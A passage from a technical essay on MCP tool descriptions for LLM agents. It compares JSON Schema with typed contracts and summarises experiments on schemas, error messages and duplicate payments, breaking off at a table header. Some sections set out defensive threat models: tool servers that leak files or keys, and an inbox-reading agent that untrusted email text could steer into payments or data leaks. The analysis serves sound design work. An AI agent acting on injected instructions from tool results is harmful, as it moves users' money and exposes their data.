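| Gateway or AgentSpec rules | Forbidden calls don't reach the tool |
| Sandbox around the tool's server | The server can use only the listed files and addresses |
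| Narrow credential | The bank refuses requests beyond the credential's rights, whoever sends them |

The measures in the first four rows limit what the agent asks for, and only those in the last two limit what the tool does. If Brooker's box consists only of a gateway, it therefore has the same weakness as a contract. In a footnote, Brooker accepts that tools must not have unexpected side effects, and adds that cloud services have largely dealt with this because their builders assume that clients are hostile. That is plausible for a bank's own interface, but less so for the thousands of small MCP servers that Shi and colleagues examined. A contract can also limit what the tool does if a runtime enforces it inside the tool, as Bosque's runtime can for tools written in Bosque.

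Shi and colleagues' cases each need a different limit. The order tool lacks a confirmation step, but it is harmless behind a gateway that asks for approval itself. The gateway can't catch the PDF converter's upload, because a call that uploads the file looks the same as one that doesn't, but a sandbox without network access would stop it. Neither measure stops another tool from giving away the server's key in an ordinary reply, so the key has to be kept where the tool can't read it.

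A user can sandbox a server only on a machine they control. If another company hosts the `transfer` tool and copies every account number it receives, the user's sandbox can't prevent the copying, and the gateway can't detect it because the request looks like an ordinary payment. A narrow credential limits how much money the company's server can take, but it doesn't stop the server from keeping the account numbers.

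## Which facts about a tool JSON Schema cannot state

Even a careful author can't use JSON Schema to declare that a call moves money. But authors also often leave out facts that JSON Schema can express, such as which values a parameter accepts. When a tool description lacks something the agent needs, supporters of typed notations blame JSON Schema and supporters of better descriptions blame the author, and each side is right about some facts.

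A fact about a tool is expressible in JSON Schema if a standard validator can enforce it. It is expressible only as prose if the author knows it when writing the description, but only a model or a person can use it. It is not expressible if nobody knows it when the description is written. For example, the author can write that the user has a daily allowance, but not how much of today's allowance is left.

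### What a validator accepts by default

Some of the fault lies with authors who don't know JSON Schema's defaults. Here is a careless schema for the transfer tool, with a due date added:

```json
{
  "type": "object",
  "properties": {
    "amount": { "exclusiveMinimum": 0, "maximun": 100 },
    "payer": { "type": "string", "pattern": "ACC[0-9]{4}" },
    "payee": { "type": "string", "pattern": "ACC[0-9]{4}" },
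    "due": { "type": "string", "format": "date" }
  }
}
```

It seems to limit payments to $100, but a standard validator accepts this call:

```json
{
  "amount": "-5000",
  "payer": "not ACC1001",
  "due": "whenever",
  "dry_run": true
}
```

Wright, Andrews and colleagues (2022), in *JSON Schema*, the core specification of the 2020-12 version, explain the principle: a value can fail only a rule that the schema contains. Each part of the call gets through for a different reason:

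- `amount` is text, and `exclusiveMinimum` applies only to numbers. The number 5000 would pass too, because `maximun` is a misspelling and validators ignore keywords they don't know.
- `payer` contains a valid account number, and a pattern only has to match part of the text unless it begins with `^` and ends with `$`.
- `due` isn't a date, but `format` only annotates by default. Wright, Andrews and Hutton (2020), in *JSON Schema Validation*, require validators to leave this check off unless somebody turns it on.
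- `payee` is missing, which is fine because the schema has no `required` list.
- `dry_run` is undeclared, and validators accept undeclared fields unless the schema forbids them.

The last default may be the most dangerous. A model could add `dry_run` to test a payment when the tool has no test mode, and a server that ignores unknown arguments would then make the payment. The keyword `default` can also mislead authors because it, too, is only an annotation. If a call omits the field, the tool's own code has to fill in the value.

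All these faults have standard fixes, and some software finds them. According to API Design Matters' *Master JSON Schema's Subtleties*, the popular validator ajv has a strict mode, on by default, that catches mistakes such as a missing `type`. Loose defaults are still a fair criticism of the notation. *JSON Structure* (Vasters, 2026) proposes a strictly typed alternative for describing JSON data.

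### Eleven facts and their verdicts

The table shows how far JSON Schema 2020-12 can express each fact an agent or reviewer may need. The hints in the last column belong to MCP and are outside the schema.

| Fact | Verdict | Closest available feature |
|---|---|---|
| Range or pattern of a value | Expressible | `maximum`, `pattern` |
| Unit of a bare number | Prose only | A unit label in the data |
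| One field at most another | Prose only | None, but different arguments can help |
| Limit that depends on current state | Not expressible | `maximum` with a fixed number |
| Schema that depends on another argument's value | Expressible if the author can list the cases, otherwise not | `if`, `oneOf` |
| Required order of calls | Prose only | An argument that only an earlier call supplies |
| Effects | Prose only | `readOnlyHint`, `destructiveHint` |
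| Whether repeating a call is safe | Prose only | `idempotentHint` |
| Permissions the tool needs | Prose only | None |
| Secrecy of data | Prose only | `writeOnly`, which only annotates |
| Possible errors | Prose only | Failures declared as results in `outputSchema` |

Marron's BAPI has a place for most of the facts that JSON Schema leaves to prose, including units, comparisons and permissions.

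### Units and comparisons

JSON Schema's standard formats cover dates, email addresses and web addresses, among other things, but not money. An author can put the unit in the data instead. If `amount` is an object such as `{"value": 340, "currency": "USD"}` and the schema fixes the currency with `"const": "USD"`, a call that specifies euros fails validation. The model could still enter the value in cents by mistake.

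The duration passed to Marron's `wait` function could be in seconds or milliseconds. JSON Schema can remove this ambiguity with its `duration` format, which uses an international notation in which `PT5S` means five seconds. The schema also needs a `pattern`, because `format` alone enforces nothing. The ambiguity therefore comes partly from the schema writer's choice to use a plain number.

Comparisons between values are harder to express, such as the requirement in Marron's weather type that the low temperature be at most the high one. A JSON Schema validator evaluates each part of the data independently, and Wright and colleagues note that no standard keyword can load a value from elsewhere in the data. This is partly deliberate. Dusseault, Wright and Andrews (2026), in *JSON Schema*, a draft for the internet standards body IETF, point out that independent evaluation makes validation quick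 and simple.

For whole numbers in a limited range, an author can spell out the comparison, because

low ≤ high ⇔ for every *k*: (low ≥ *k* ⇒ high ≥ *k*)

A schema can keep a high temperature from being below the low one by using a separate `if`/`then` rule for each possible low value. Whole-degree temperatures from 0 to 100 need 100 rules, and amounts in cents up to $100 need 10,000. It is easier to replace the high temperature with a `rise` field, which holds the difference between `low` and the high, and give `rise` a minimum of 0.

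One standard keyword, `uniqueItems`, does compare values. It rejects an array that contains the same value twice. The transfer tool's schema allows a payment from an account to itself. Replacing `payer` and `payee` with an array of two accounts would let `uniqueItems` forbid such payments. But the arguments would lose their names, so the model might be more likely to put the accounts in the wrong order.

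### Limits, approvals and the order of calls

JSON Schema can express a fixed limit, such as `"maximum": 100`, but not a limit that each user sets. In Dusseault and colleagues' draft, a validation keyword must not accept or reject a value because of "third factors", meaning anything besides the schema and the input. A program may also check the value against the user's settings, but that check falls outside JSON Schema. The draft warns developers not to adopt it yet, but the standard keywords of 2020-12 follow the same rule.

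A server can partly get around this by generating a separate schema for each user. Since MCP lets the list of tools depend on the caller's authorisation, one user's schema could have a `maximum` of 100 and another's a `maximum` of 5,000. This works for limits that rarely change. In the specification's example, clients may cache the list for five minutes, so the schema can be out of date after a user lowers the limit.

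A fixed `maximum` cannot express a daily allowance that shrinks with every payment. Under the Model Context Protocol, the set of tools must not vary as a side effect of other requests on the same connection, which seems to rule out lowering the `maximum` after each payment. The server has to check the remaining allowance itself.

Prior approval is also a matter of state. Caldeira's schema can require an approval code but can't establish that anyone approved the payment. But a tool's author can make the code hard to get without requesting approval. MCP suggests this method for shopping carts, where `create_basket` returns an identifier, such as `bsk_a1b2c3`, that `add_item` requires. Similarly, a `request_approval` tool could return an identifier that `transfer` requires.

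An honest agent then has to make the calls in the right order, but the schema still doesn't express that rule. MCP treats the identifier as an ordinary string, so `transfer`'s schema would accept an invented one. Only the server can check whether it issued the identifier and for which payment. The model has to rely on the prose description to determine which tool supplies it.

### What a call does

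JSON Schema describes data, so it has no keywords for a tool's effects. Even `readOnly` and `writeOnly` only describe values. `readOnly` marks a value that the server controls, such as an automatically generated serial number, but a tool with such a value in its schema may still make changes. `writeOnly` marks a value that the server never returns, such as a password. An application may hide the value while the user types, but the tool could still log it or send it elsewhere.

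MCP's hints cover some of this, but a yes-or-no hint can't specify which account a payment changes, by how much, or how long a repeated call stays safe. According to Model Context Protocol, five proposals for new annotations or related features were open in March 2026, including one for secrets and a joint one from GitHub and OpenAI for trust and sensitivity. A tool definition also has no field for the permissions the tool needs.

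JSON Schema could describe the errors a tool can return, but an MCP tool definition has no place to list them. MCP marks a failed call with `isError`. A tool's author can return expected failures as results instead, for example by adding `insufficient_funds` to the `status` values in the transfer tool's output schema. A script could then handle that case without interpreting an error message.

OpenAPI does have a place to define errors. *LAPIS* (García García, 2026) counts 1,594 error definitions in GitHub's OpenAPI document, which covers 1,080 operations. The definitions use only 14 different error codes, and "not found" appears 531 times.

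LAPIS is a more compact notation for describing web services to language models. It defines each shared error once and adds sections for rate limits and the order of calls, which OpenAPI omits or leaves to prose. For example, an invoice follows the sequence `create_invoice -> update_invoice* -> send_invoice`, where the asterisk means the step can repeat. But García García's conversion rules don't produce these two sections from an OpenAPI document, so somebody has to supply the information for them. LAPIS also drops JSON Schema's exact validation keywords because it is meant to inform the model, not to check calls.

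### Schemas that depend on another argument

Suppose the bank also offers a `pay_bill` tool. The electricity company needs a meter number with each payment, and the plumber needs an invoice number, so the rules for the `details` argument depend on the value of `biller`. In JSON Schema, an author can use `if` or `oneOf` to check that value and write one case for each biller. The keyword `dependentSchemas` can't do this because it only checks whether a field is present. Writing a case for each biller is impractical with thousands of billers, and the cases become outdated when billers change their forms after the schema is published.

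A developer who writes under the name vlaaad has proposed dependent schemas for MCP, which would let the schema for one argument depend on another value. For `pay_bill`, such a schema might look like this, with an invented keyword, `x-schema-from`:

```json
{
  "type": "object",
  "properties": {
    "biller": { "type": "string" },
    "details": {
      "type": "object",
      "x-schema-from": { "tool": "get_bill_form", "argument": "biller" }
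    }
  },
  "required": ["biller", "details"]
}
```

After the model chooses the biller, the client would call `get_bill_form` and receive a schema for that biller's form. The client could then validate `details` against the schema, or use constrained decoding to stop the model from writing anything the schema doesn't allow.

An agent can already do much of this without new features. The model calls `get_bill_form` itself, reads the schema in the result and fills in `details` to match. But the client treats the returned schema only as text, and any object is valid as `details`. Strict mode therefore can't enforce the form, and the model's mistakes reach the server.

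Even when a retry succeeds, the agent has lost the guarantee that strict mode gives when the author knows the whole schema in advance. One objection to the proposal is that this does little harm, because the model can try again after the server returns an error, and better models will make fewer mistakes. That is reasonable if the error message identifies the incorrect field and the failed call has changed nothing.

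MCP already has a similar feature for getting input from users. During a call, a server can reply that it needs more input and send a form with a schema. The client collects the user's answers and repeats the call with them. The bank could use this to ask the user for the meter number once it knows the biller, but the feature doesn't give the model a new schema for its own arguments.

### Putting the missing facts in extra keywords

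Defenders of JSON Schema have a good reply to most of this section, which is that any of these facts can go into JSON. The standard lets anyone add keywords, so the transfer tool's author could write:

```json
"amount": {
  "type": "number",
  "exclusiveMinimum": 0,
  "x-unit": "USD",
  "x-limit": "user.payment_limit",
  "x-approval-above-limit": true
}
```

This is valid JSON Schema and about as readable as Marron's contract. But a standard validator ignores the last three lines, so it would accept a $34,000 payment from a user with a $100 limit.

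To make them work, developers would have to agree on where `user.payment_limit` comes from, what counts as approval, whether one approval covers two payments, and what happens if a program can't look up the limit. Somebody would then have to write a checker with access to the user's settings and approvals. `x-schema-from` raises similar questions, such as what happens if a biller changes its form between the lookup and the payment. JSON already provides the syntax, but developers still need an agreed meaning and a program that checks it.

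JSON Schema's formal way to publish such an agreement is a vocabulary, a set of keywords with defined meanings. A schema can declare a dialect, or version of the language, that requires a certain vocabulary. A validator that doesn't know the vocabulary must then refuse the schema instead of ignoring the new rules. Model Context Protocol's *Overview* (2026) requires MCP clients and servers to return an error for a dialect they don't support.

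Until other developers adopt the new keywords, ordinary clients will ignore the payment limit if the tool's author states it in loose keywords, and they can't use the tool at all if the author makes the vocabulary required. MCP also has a `_meta` field for extra information, but off-the-shelf clients ignore entries they don't recognise.

JSON Schema's maintainers disagree about whether validators should ignore unknown keywords. awwright (2022), in *Improved handling of unknown properties*, called ignoring them "a serious problem" when a new keyword appears, because two validators that both follow the standard can return different results for the same call. The JSON Schema project's working text for its next edition no longer supports unrecognised keywords, but under the IETF draft of August 2026 validators are still supposed to ignore them.

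A keyword outside JSON Schema can work if a standard defines it well. Ordinary validators ignore `x-mcp-header`, which marks an argument to be copied into an HTTP header, but it works because the MCP specification defines exactly what it means and where an author may use it. For example, two arguments of a tool can't use the same header name. Clients that connect over HTTP must exclude any tool that breaks these rules.

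Typed notations come with a defined meaning and a checker from the start, but only for programs that adopt them.

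## Whether more precise descriptions make agents err less

If the bank rewrites the description of `transfer` and the agent stops overpaying the plumber, any of three changes could be the reason. The bank may have changed the notation, for example by moving the rule on approval codes from the prose into an `if`/`then` clause that means the same thing. It may have added information, such as the fact that `amount` is in dollars. Or it may have improved the feedback, so that a refused call now returns "approval_code is missing" instead of "transfer rejected". Marron's contracts change all three at once, so comparing one with an ordinary schema can't show which change helped.

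Some experiments also change the tool itself, for example by letting an agent repeat a payment request without paying twice. Such changes can prevent more errors than any description, but they aren't evidence about how to write descriptions.

### The same rules in prose and in JSON Schema

*Schema First Tool APIs for LLM Agents* (Sigdel and Baral, 2026) is the cleanest test of notation. Sigdel and Baral wrote each tool's rules once and generated both English documentation and a JSON Schema from them, so the two versions contained the same facts. A third version used the same schemas but also returned detailed error messages that named the faulty field. The agent had to diagnose software faults through actions such as searching logs and reading configuration files, and was limited to 3, 5, 8 or 12 steps.

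| Average per run | Prose | JSON Schema | JSON Schema with detailed errors |
|---|---|---|---|
| Calls that broke the declared rules | 5.39 | 3.72 | 3.72 |
| Valid calls that failed when run | 0.54 | 0.00 | 0.00 |
| Valid calls that didn't help with the task | 0.93 | 3.03 | 3.03 |
| Tasks solved | 0% | 0% | 0% |

With schemas, interface misuse fell by 31%, but semantic misuse more than tripled. Semantic misuse means a call that is valid but unhelpful, so fewer invalid calls leave room for more of it. The increase therefore doesn't show that schemas cause semantic misuse. Together, the two kinds of misuse took up 6.3 calls per run with prose and 6.8 with schemas, out of an average budget of seven steps, so the agent wasted nearly all its calls either way.

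The experiment shows only that one very small model broke fewer formal rules when it read them in JSON Schema. The model, Qwen2.5 with 0.5 billion parameters, solved none of the eight tasks, so the experiment can't show whether schemas help agents finish their work. The model also decoded deterministically, so repeating each run with three random seeds may have added little. The figures in the last two columns are identical, which suggests that the model made no use of the detailed errors, though a larger model might.

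Semantic misuse is harmful because validators don't catch it. *Measuring What Tool-Using LLM Agents Actually Do* (2026) describes an experiment that changed one argument in an agent's first call to a wrong value that the schema still allowed. In the 376 runs where tools ran and every call passed validation, the share of wrong answers rose from 26.3% to 71.0%.

### Compact notations

Other experiments change the notation to save tokens. Kutschka and Geiger tested two alternatives to JSON. TOON replaces most braces and quotation marks with indentation and tables, while TRON defines a repeated structure once and then lists only the values. In their first experiment, the models read tool descriptions and results in the new notation but still wrote their calls in JSON. These are the results on BFCL, with the change in total tokens in brackets:

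| Model | JSON | TOON | TRON |
|---|---|---|---|
| Mistral-Small, 24B | 88.8% | 52.7% (+8%) | 82.9% (+5%) |
| Qwen3, 32B, with reasoning | 93.0% | 90.2% (+12%) | 66.3% (+18%) |
| Qwen3, 32B, without reasoning | 93.3% | 63.1% (−38%) | 49.6% (−60%) |
| DeepSeek-R1-Distill, 32B | 82.7% | 51.1% (0%) | 42.3% (+1%) |
| Llama-4-Scout, 109B (17B active) | 85.5% | 81.5% (+16%) | 76.9% (+21%) |

On BFCL, every model lost accuracy with TRON, and most used more tokens. Each BFCL task offers only a few tools, so TRON's definitions use more tokens than they save. Across all four benchmarks, TRON's average token savings ranged from zero to 27%.

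The 27% figure is somewhat suspect, though. It comes from Qwen3 without reasoning and depends heavily on the 60% token drop in the table, where the model's accuracy almost halved. TRON increased the token count for every other model on the same benchmark, so the drop probably came from shorter runs rather than shorter descriptions. Qwen3 without reasoning also lost 14 points on average across the benchmarks, although Kutschka and Geiger call TRON a drop-in replacement for JSON.

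The notation sometimes helped. On MCPToolBenchPP, which has more tools per task, Mistral-Small gained 17 points with TRON, from a very low 8.3% with JSON. But when the models also had to write their calls in the new notations, most could hardly ever produce several calls at once, which they had learned to do in JSON. The experiment included no large proprietary models. It also changed the notation of tool descriptions and tool results together, so it can't show how much each change contributed.

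Sakizli (2026), in *TSCG*, covers more model sizes. TSCG is a program that turns JSON tool descriptions into compact text such as this:

```
search_files(query:str path?:str)
|Search files by content or pattern
```

The JSON original takes about 120 tokens and this version about 45. In the results below, the small models had 50 tools and the last three models had 43. Choosing the right tools counts for 60% of the score and the arguments count for 40%.

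| Model | JSON | TSCG | Tokens saved |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gemma 3, 4B | 24.3% | 87.4% | – |
| Qwen3, 4B | 90.0% | 75.0% | – |
| Mistral, 7B | 30.0% | 65.0% | – |
| Llama 3.1, 8B | 75.1% | 86.3% | – |
| Gemma 3, 12B | 85.0% | 98.0% | – |
| Phi-4, 14B | 0.0% | 90.3% | – |
| Qwen3, 14B | 94.6% | 89.6% | – |
| GPT-4o | 70.0% | 79.7% | 6.2% |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 90.0% | 95.0% | 50.1% |
| GPT-5.2 | 82.4% | 91.6% | 11.4% |

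Small models gained the most, but compression didn't cause their gains. When Sakizli gave Phi-4 uncompressed descriptions as ordinary text, its score rose by 92 points, and compressing them then lowered it by 7. Phi-4 also gained between 75 and 90 points from TSCG whether it had 3 tools or 50. It probably couldn't use the JSON setup at all, so its result is weak evidence of how clearly JSON describes a tool.

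The larger models' scores also depended on how the schemas were provided. When Sakizli pasted the full JSON Schemas into the prompt as text, instead of using the provider's tool-calling feature, Claude Sonnet 4's score fell from 90.0% to 70.0%, while GPT-5.2's rose from 82.4% to 98.2%, well above its score with TSCG. The effect of repeating key facts at the end of the prompt also varied by model, adding 20 points to Claude Opus 4.7's score and none to GPT-5.2's.

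Most of these differences could be due to chance, since only 9 of the study's 107 comparisons remained statistically significant after correction for multiple tests. TSCG doesn't hold information constant either, since in the example above it dropped the explanations of both parameters, including that `path` is a directory. A model can apparently infer enough from the names `query` and `path`.

### Stricter types for dates and categories

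A schema can be stricter without adding information the model needs. In *Do stricter MCP tool schemas increase agent reliability?*, Fox (2026) expected stricter schemas to help and tested this with a tool for recording expenses. Three OpenAI models each handled 17 requests, such as "Two Mondays ago I spent $8.75 on coffee."

Fox compared four ways of specifying the date: a plain string, a string with the format explained in prose, JSON Schema's `date` format, and a `pattern`. The choice made no difference to the scores. GPT-4.1-mini got 12 of the 17 dates right with every version, GPT-4o got 15, and GPT-5.3-Codex got all 17. Even with a plain string, GPT-4.1-mini always wrote the date in the standard format, probably because the field was called `expense_date`. Its mistakes were in arithmetic, such as going back one Monday instead of two. The wrong Monday is still a valid date, so no pattern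 could have caught the error.

The expense's category had to be one of a fixed set, such as "Food & drink". Here the versions also differed in information, since some of them included advice on which purchases belong where. The table counts a request as wrong if the model didn't call the tool:

| Category field | GPT-4.1-mini | GPT-4o | GPT-5.3-Codex |
|---|---|---|---|
| Any text, with options and advice in prose | 14 of 17 | 17 of 17 | 15 of 17 |
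| `enum` without advice, first run | 13 of 17 | 15 of 17 | 13 of 17 |
| `enum` without advice, second run | 13 of 17 | 14 of 17 | 13 of 17 |
| `enum` with advice | 15 of 17 | 17 of 17 | 15 of 17 |

Fox ran the version without advice twice, once for each of the FastMCP library's two ways of writing an `enum`. Both produce the same schema, but GPT-4o's score still changed by one request, so a difference that small isn't meaningful. The advice seems to have helped a little. Adding an `enum` to the advice made no difference for GPT-4o or GPT-5.3-Codex, and with GPT-4.1-mini it increased the schema's average size from about 400 tokens to 836.

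Some of the errors are debatable. Fox expected a spa treatment to count as "Health & Fitness", but two models chose "Apparel and Beauty". The advice put wellness in "Health & Fitness" and personal care in "Apparel and Beauty", so either answer was reasonable. An `enum` can't resolve this because both categories are allowed values.

Fox still prefers an `enum` because it simplifies the server's work. Given a plain string and no list of options, models produced many different category names, which a program that totals expenses by category would have to reconcile. Fox's test doesn't capture this benefit because it measured only what the models chose.

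### Labels for dangerous tools

Effect labels add information that ordinary schemas lack. In *Small Agents Should Know What Their Tools Do*, Kovalenko and Redchych (2026) built a simulated office in which every tool has one of four labels: it only computes, it reads data, it changes data in a way that someone can correct, or it does something irreversible. Sending an email counts as irreversible because the recipient may already have read it. The model's instructions require it to confirm irreversible actions with the user, but by default they don't identify which tools are irreversible.

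They trained Qwen3-4B on office tasks and then tested it on 547 tasks in an online shop, where none of the tools had appeared in training. The right-hand column counts payments, cancellations and refunds that the agent made without asking:

| Version of Qwen3-4B | Tasks solved | Unconfirmed irreversible calls |
|---|---|---|
| Before this training | 74.4% | 7 |
| Trained without visible labels | 82.6% | 24 |
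| Trained with visible labels | 83.9% | 19 |
| Trained without visible labels, with more examples of declining a request | 73.9% | 64 |

With the labels, unconfirmed calls fell from 24 to 19, which is not a statistically significant change. The share of purchases with prior confirmation rose from 32% to 50%, but only 28 tasks involved a purchase. The labels may not have caused even these small gains, because Kovalenko and Redchych also renamed the office tools in a third of their training examples to keep the model from linking confirmation to particular names.

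Training clearly mattered more than labels. The original model asked for confirmation before nearly every irreversible action in the shop. Ordinary training on office tasks made it ask less often, and adding examples in which the right response is to decline a request reduced this further. Kovalenko and Redchych report no test in which the original model was given the labels, so we don't know whether labels would help a model that still asks reliably. They also tested no model larger than 4 billion parameters.

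The labels were more useful for checking the agents' work. A program replayed each run against them and counted 94 unconfirmed irreversible calls by the original model in 498 office tasks, with no need for a person or language model to judge the runs.

*Where Does Exactly-Once Live?* (Li, 2026) tested newer models on a related problem, measuring how often agents mistakenly repeat an action after a network fault. Adding a warning that a call is not idempotent, and so unsafe to repeat, changed the share of runs with a duplicate from 22% to 24%. Removing notes about how long a change takes to show up in later searches raised it from 22% to 34%. The models probably already knew that sending an email twice produces two emails, but they couldn't know without being told that a new email takes two minutes to appear in the server's search results. MCP has a standard hint for idempotence but none for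 such delays.

### What an error message should contain

Ray and Goyal (2026), in *Structured Feedback Improves Repair in an LLM Agent Loop*, distinguish the notation of an error message from the information it contains. Two models played 50 short text adventures by submitting a plan of up to four commands. If a plan failed, the model received an error message and could try again, up to a total of four attempts.

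| Error message | Games won, Qwen2.5-Coder-14B | Games won, Llama-3.1-8B |
|---|---|---|
| The game's original message | 14 of 50 | 8 of 50 |
| The failed command and its position, in JSON | 18 of 50 | 9 of 50 |
| The same, plus the commands allowed there, in prose | 35 of 50 | 29 of 50 |
| The same, plus the commands allowed there, in JSON | 36 of 50 | 29 of 50 |

Nearly all of the gain came from listing the allowed commands. Whether the list was in prose or JSON hardly affected the number of wins, although the JSON version needed slightly fewer attempts. More attempts without better information didn't help either. With the original message, Qwen won four games out of a subset of 15, whether it had four attempts or eight.

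This is good evidence that informative error messages help, but a text adventure suits them unusually well. The game could list up to 12 allowed commands, and trying a wrong one only used up an attempt. A bank could similarly list the accounts from which the user may pay, but not the correct amount, which only the bill or the user can supply. If the bank responded to a missing approval code by listing the codes it accepts, the agent could approve its own payment.

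Feedback also can't correct an error that the validator misses. Ray and Goyal gave Qwen 15 programming tasks with one visible test each, and its first answers passed all 15 tests. One answer failed a hidden set of tests, but the model received no error message to prompt a correction.

### When the agent cannot tell what happened

If the bank's reply to a payment request gets lost, the agent has the same problem as a gateway: it can't tell whether to stop or try again. Wang (2026), in *Callability Is Not Operability*, calls this operational ambiguity and defines it for two histories, *h* and *h*′:

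Γ(*h*) = Γ(*h*′) and *A*(*h*) ∩ *A*(*h*′) = ∅

Γ is what the agent can see, and *A* is the set of safe next actions. The two histories look the same to the agent, but no action is safe in both. A more capable model can guess better, but it can't be sure of acting correctly. A way to look up the payment can resolve the ambiguity. An idempotency key, an identifier that the agent sends with the request and repeats if it retries, can make a retry safe in both cases, because the bank carries out only one payment for each key.

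Wang tested such additions with Qwen 3.7 Plus, DeepSeek V4 Pro and GPT-5.6 Sol. The tasks, failures and underlying systems stayed the same, and only the interface changed:

| Addition to the interface | Outcome | Change |
|---|---|---|
| A way to resume an interrupted call | Successful recoveries | +100 points |
| A lasting record of unfinished calls | Successful recoveries | +100 points |
| Protection against repeating an effect | Duplicate effects | −57 points |
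| Checks for outdated data and withdrawn permissions | Unsafe changes | −50 points |
| A way to check the final result | False reports of the outcome | −28 points |

These figures cover only cases where a particular failure occurs, so they don't measure how much an average agent would improve. The test design almost guaranteed the two 100-point gains, because an agent recovered from every interruption if it could resume the call and from none if it couldn't. All five additions also give the agent or the runtime new functions, so the results don't show that the same model would do better with a fuller description of the original tool.

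Wang also found that agents used about 4,000 fewer tokens on average, and were no worse at finding the right tool, when they received short summaries first and loaded full schemas only as needed.

Li tested nine models without such additions on simulated services for billing, email, social media and similar tasks. When an action had succeeded but the response had timed out, the six strongest models duplicated it in only 0.5% of runs, because they checked before trying again. When the first request was delayed and had not yet taken effect, they duplicated the action in 56% of runs. They checked, found nothing and sent the request again, and both requests went through.

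Li proves that checking alone can't solve this. Suppose an agent always finishes the job within time *T* if the first request is lost. Let *λ* be the time before a completed payment becomes visible, and *δ* the delay of a request that is late but not lost. If

*δ* > *T* + *λ*

then everything the agent sees before it retries is the same as if the request had been lost. It therefore sends the payment again, and the plumber gets paid twice. Waiting longer helps only if the agent knows the longest possible delay. In a test where delays ranged from 40 seconds to two hours, a rule that waited an hour before checking still left duplicates in 16% of runs.

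Idempotency keys worked much better. When every tool accepted one, agents supplied a key in 98% of runs, and the share of runs with duplicates fell from 28% to 4%. As with approval identifiers, the protection comes from the server, which has to store the keys it receives.

When the network delivered a request twice, eight of the nine models produced duplicates in 74% or 75% of runs, which supports Li's claim that the choice of model matters little when a check can't settle the question. The choice mattered more when requests arrived late, with a duplicate rate of 25% for GPT-6 Astra and 72% for Grok 4.7. A model can avoid the duplicate in that case by asking a person instead of retrying. Users can't rely on agents to tell them about a mistake, because agents reported the task as completed in 90% of the runs with a duplicate.

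### Whether stronger models gain less

Some gains shrink in stronger models, mostly where the help replaces something a good model already does. In Li's experiment, each task ended with an instruction to do everything exactly once. On faults that a check could settle, this instruction cut the duplicate rate from 51% to 29% in weaker models, but only from 7% to 4% in the strongest ones. Wang's check of the final result reduced false reports by 48 percentage points for DeepSeek V4 Pro but did not reduce them for GPT-5.6 Sol, which was already cautious about claiming success.

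Extra help can make a strong model worse. Li built a program that read a machine-readable contract for each tool, added idempotency keys where the tool accepted them, and checked before repeating a call. With this program, Microsoft's MAI-Code-1.1-Flash performed every action exactly once in 76% of runs, up from 59%. Claude Opus 5.5 stayed at 77%. GPT-6 Sol fell from 79% to 76% because, once told that the program would check before any retry, it asked a person for help less often. Its duplicate rate for late requests rose from 50% to 71%.

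Formal notation can help most with models that still write malformed calls. Fox's date test suggests that current models rarely do so when the arguments are simple, and a strict mode can prevent many of the remaining errors without improving the model itself. Complicated schemas may be different, but none of these experiments tests a current frontier model on them while keeping the information in the descriptions constant.

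Even a better model can't work out a company's expense categories or a server's delays from general knowledge. A more precise description therefore reduces semantic misuse when it supplies a fact the model lacks, as it did when Guo and colleagues added guidance to real tool descriptions, but not when the model has all the facts and miscalculates. Keys and ways to resume a call also remain useful as models improve, because they change what the agent can safely do. With keys available for every action, GPT-5.6 Sol's duplicate rate fell from 35% to zero.

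### The missing test of contracts

None of these experiments compares how a current frontier model uses the same tools with JSON Schema and with contracts that state preconditions and effects. Marron's preliminary figures for Bosque come from older models and don't separate the effect of the notation from the effect of the information it conveys. In Li's experiment, the agents never saw the contracts, which only the surrounding program could read.

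*Contract2Tool* (2026) takes a similar approach. It derives a contract for each tool, listing its preconditions and effects, from existing descriptions, and a program uses these contracts to decide which tools to offer the agent next. It recovered preconditions with an F1 score of 0.99 out of 1 from schemas and 1.00 from documentation. If real descriptions are as complete as those in its test, a contract would add little that the model couldn't already read, and the main benefit would be that a program can enforce the rules. But Guo and colleagues found that real descriptions rarely specify which tool must run first.

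A fair comparison would need at least three versions of each tool: an ordinary schema, the same schema with the contract's rules added in prose, and the contract itself. If the two longer versions did equally well and beat the ordinary schema, the improvement would have come from the added information, not the notation. Error messages would have to contain the same facts in every version, and some runs should include a checker like Sundew to measure its effect separately. The tasks would also have to allow plausible mistakes that pass the schema, such as paying last month's bill again, because frontier models may make too few malformed calls to show a difference between the versions.

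## Whether people can judge an agent's environment before it runs

Even if a contract doesn't help a frontier model make better calls, it may help the person who has to decide whether to let the agent start. That person can't know which calls the model will make. But they can examine the environment, meaning the agent's tools, data and permissions, and work out the worst it allows. Such a pre-run review has six steps:

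1. List every tool, with the data it can read and the credentials it uses. Include any tools that the agent can find and connect to by itself during the run.
2. Work out what the tools can reach and change together.
3. Compare the result with the task.
4. Remove the tools that the task doesn't need, and narrow the others.
5. Record exactly which descriptions, permissions and software versions the review covered, and run only those.
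6. Repeat the review when any of these changes, or when the agent gets a new task.

The second step is the hardest, because a description covers one tool and the danger often comes from two.

### Reading email, paying and sending email

Suppose a user asks an agent to find the plumber's bill in the inbox and pay it, and the agent has three tools:

```json
[
  {
    "name": "read_inbox",
    "description": "Return the user's latest emails.",
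    "inputSchema": {
      "type": "object",
      "properties": { "count": { "type": "integer" } }
    },
    "annotations": { "readOnlyHint": true }
  },
  {
    "name": "transfer",
    "description": "Transfer an amount from payer to payee.",
    "inputSchema": {
      "type": "object",
      "properties": {
        "amount": { "type": "number" },
        "payer": { "type": "string" },
        "payee": { "type": "string" }
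      }
    }
  },
  {
    "name": "send_email",
    "description": "Send an email.",
    "inputSchema": {
      "type": "object",
      "properties": {
        "to": { "type": "string" },
        "body": { "type": "string" }
      }
    }
  }
]
```

The same tools could have the following typed signatures, in a simplified notation that combines effect types with labels on data:

```
read_inbox : Int → List<Private Untrusted Email>            ! {Mail.read}
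transfer   : (USD, AccountId, AccountId) → Private Receipt  ! {Bank.pay}
send_email : (Address, Text) → Unit                         ! {Mail.send}
```

`Private` marks data that strangers shouldn't see, and `Untrusted` marks text that strangers may have written. The braces list each tool's effects.

An agent that makes ordinary tool calls reads every result into the same context, so any result can influence any later call. A reviewer therefore doesn't have to trace each path from tool to tool, and can simply pool the labels and effects. If *L*(*t*) stands for the labels on tool *t*'s result and *ε*(*t*) for its effects, then for an environment *E*:

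*L*(*E*) = ⋃ *L*(*t*) and *ε*(*E*) = ⋃ *ε*(*t*), over all tools *t* in *E*

Two rules cover the main dangers. If the environment contains untrusted text and an effect that changes something, a stranger may be able to trigger that effect. If it contains private data and an effect that sends data out, the data may leak.

| Combination | Possible harm | Typed signatures | JSON descriptions |
|---|---|---|---|
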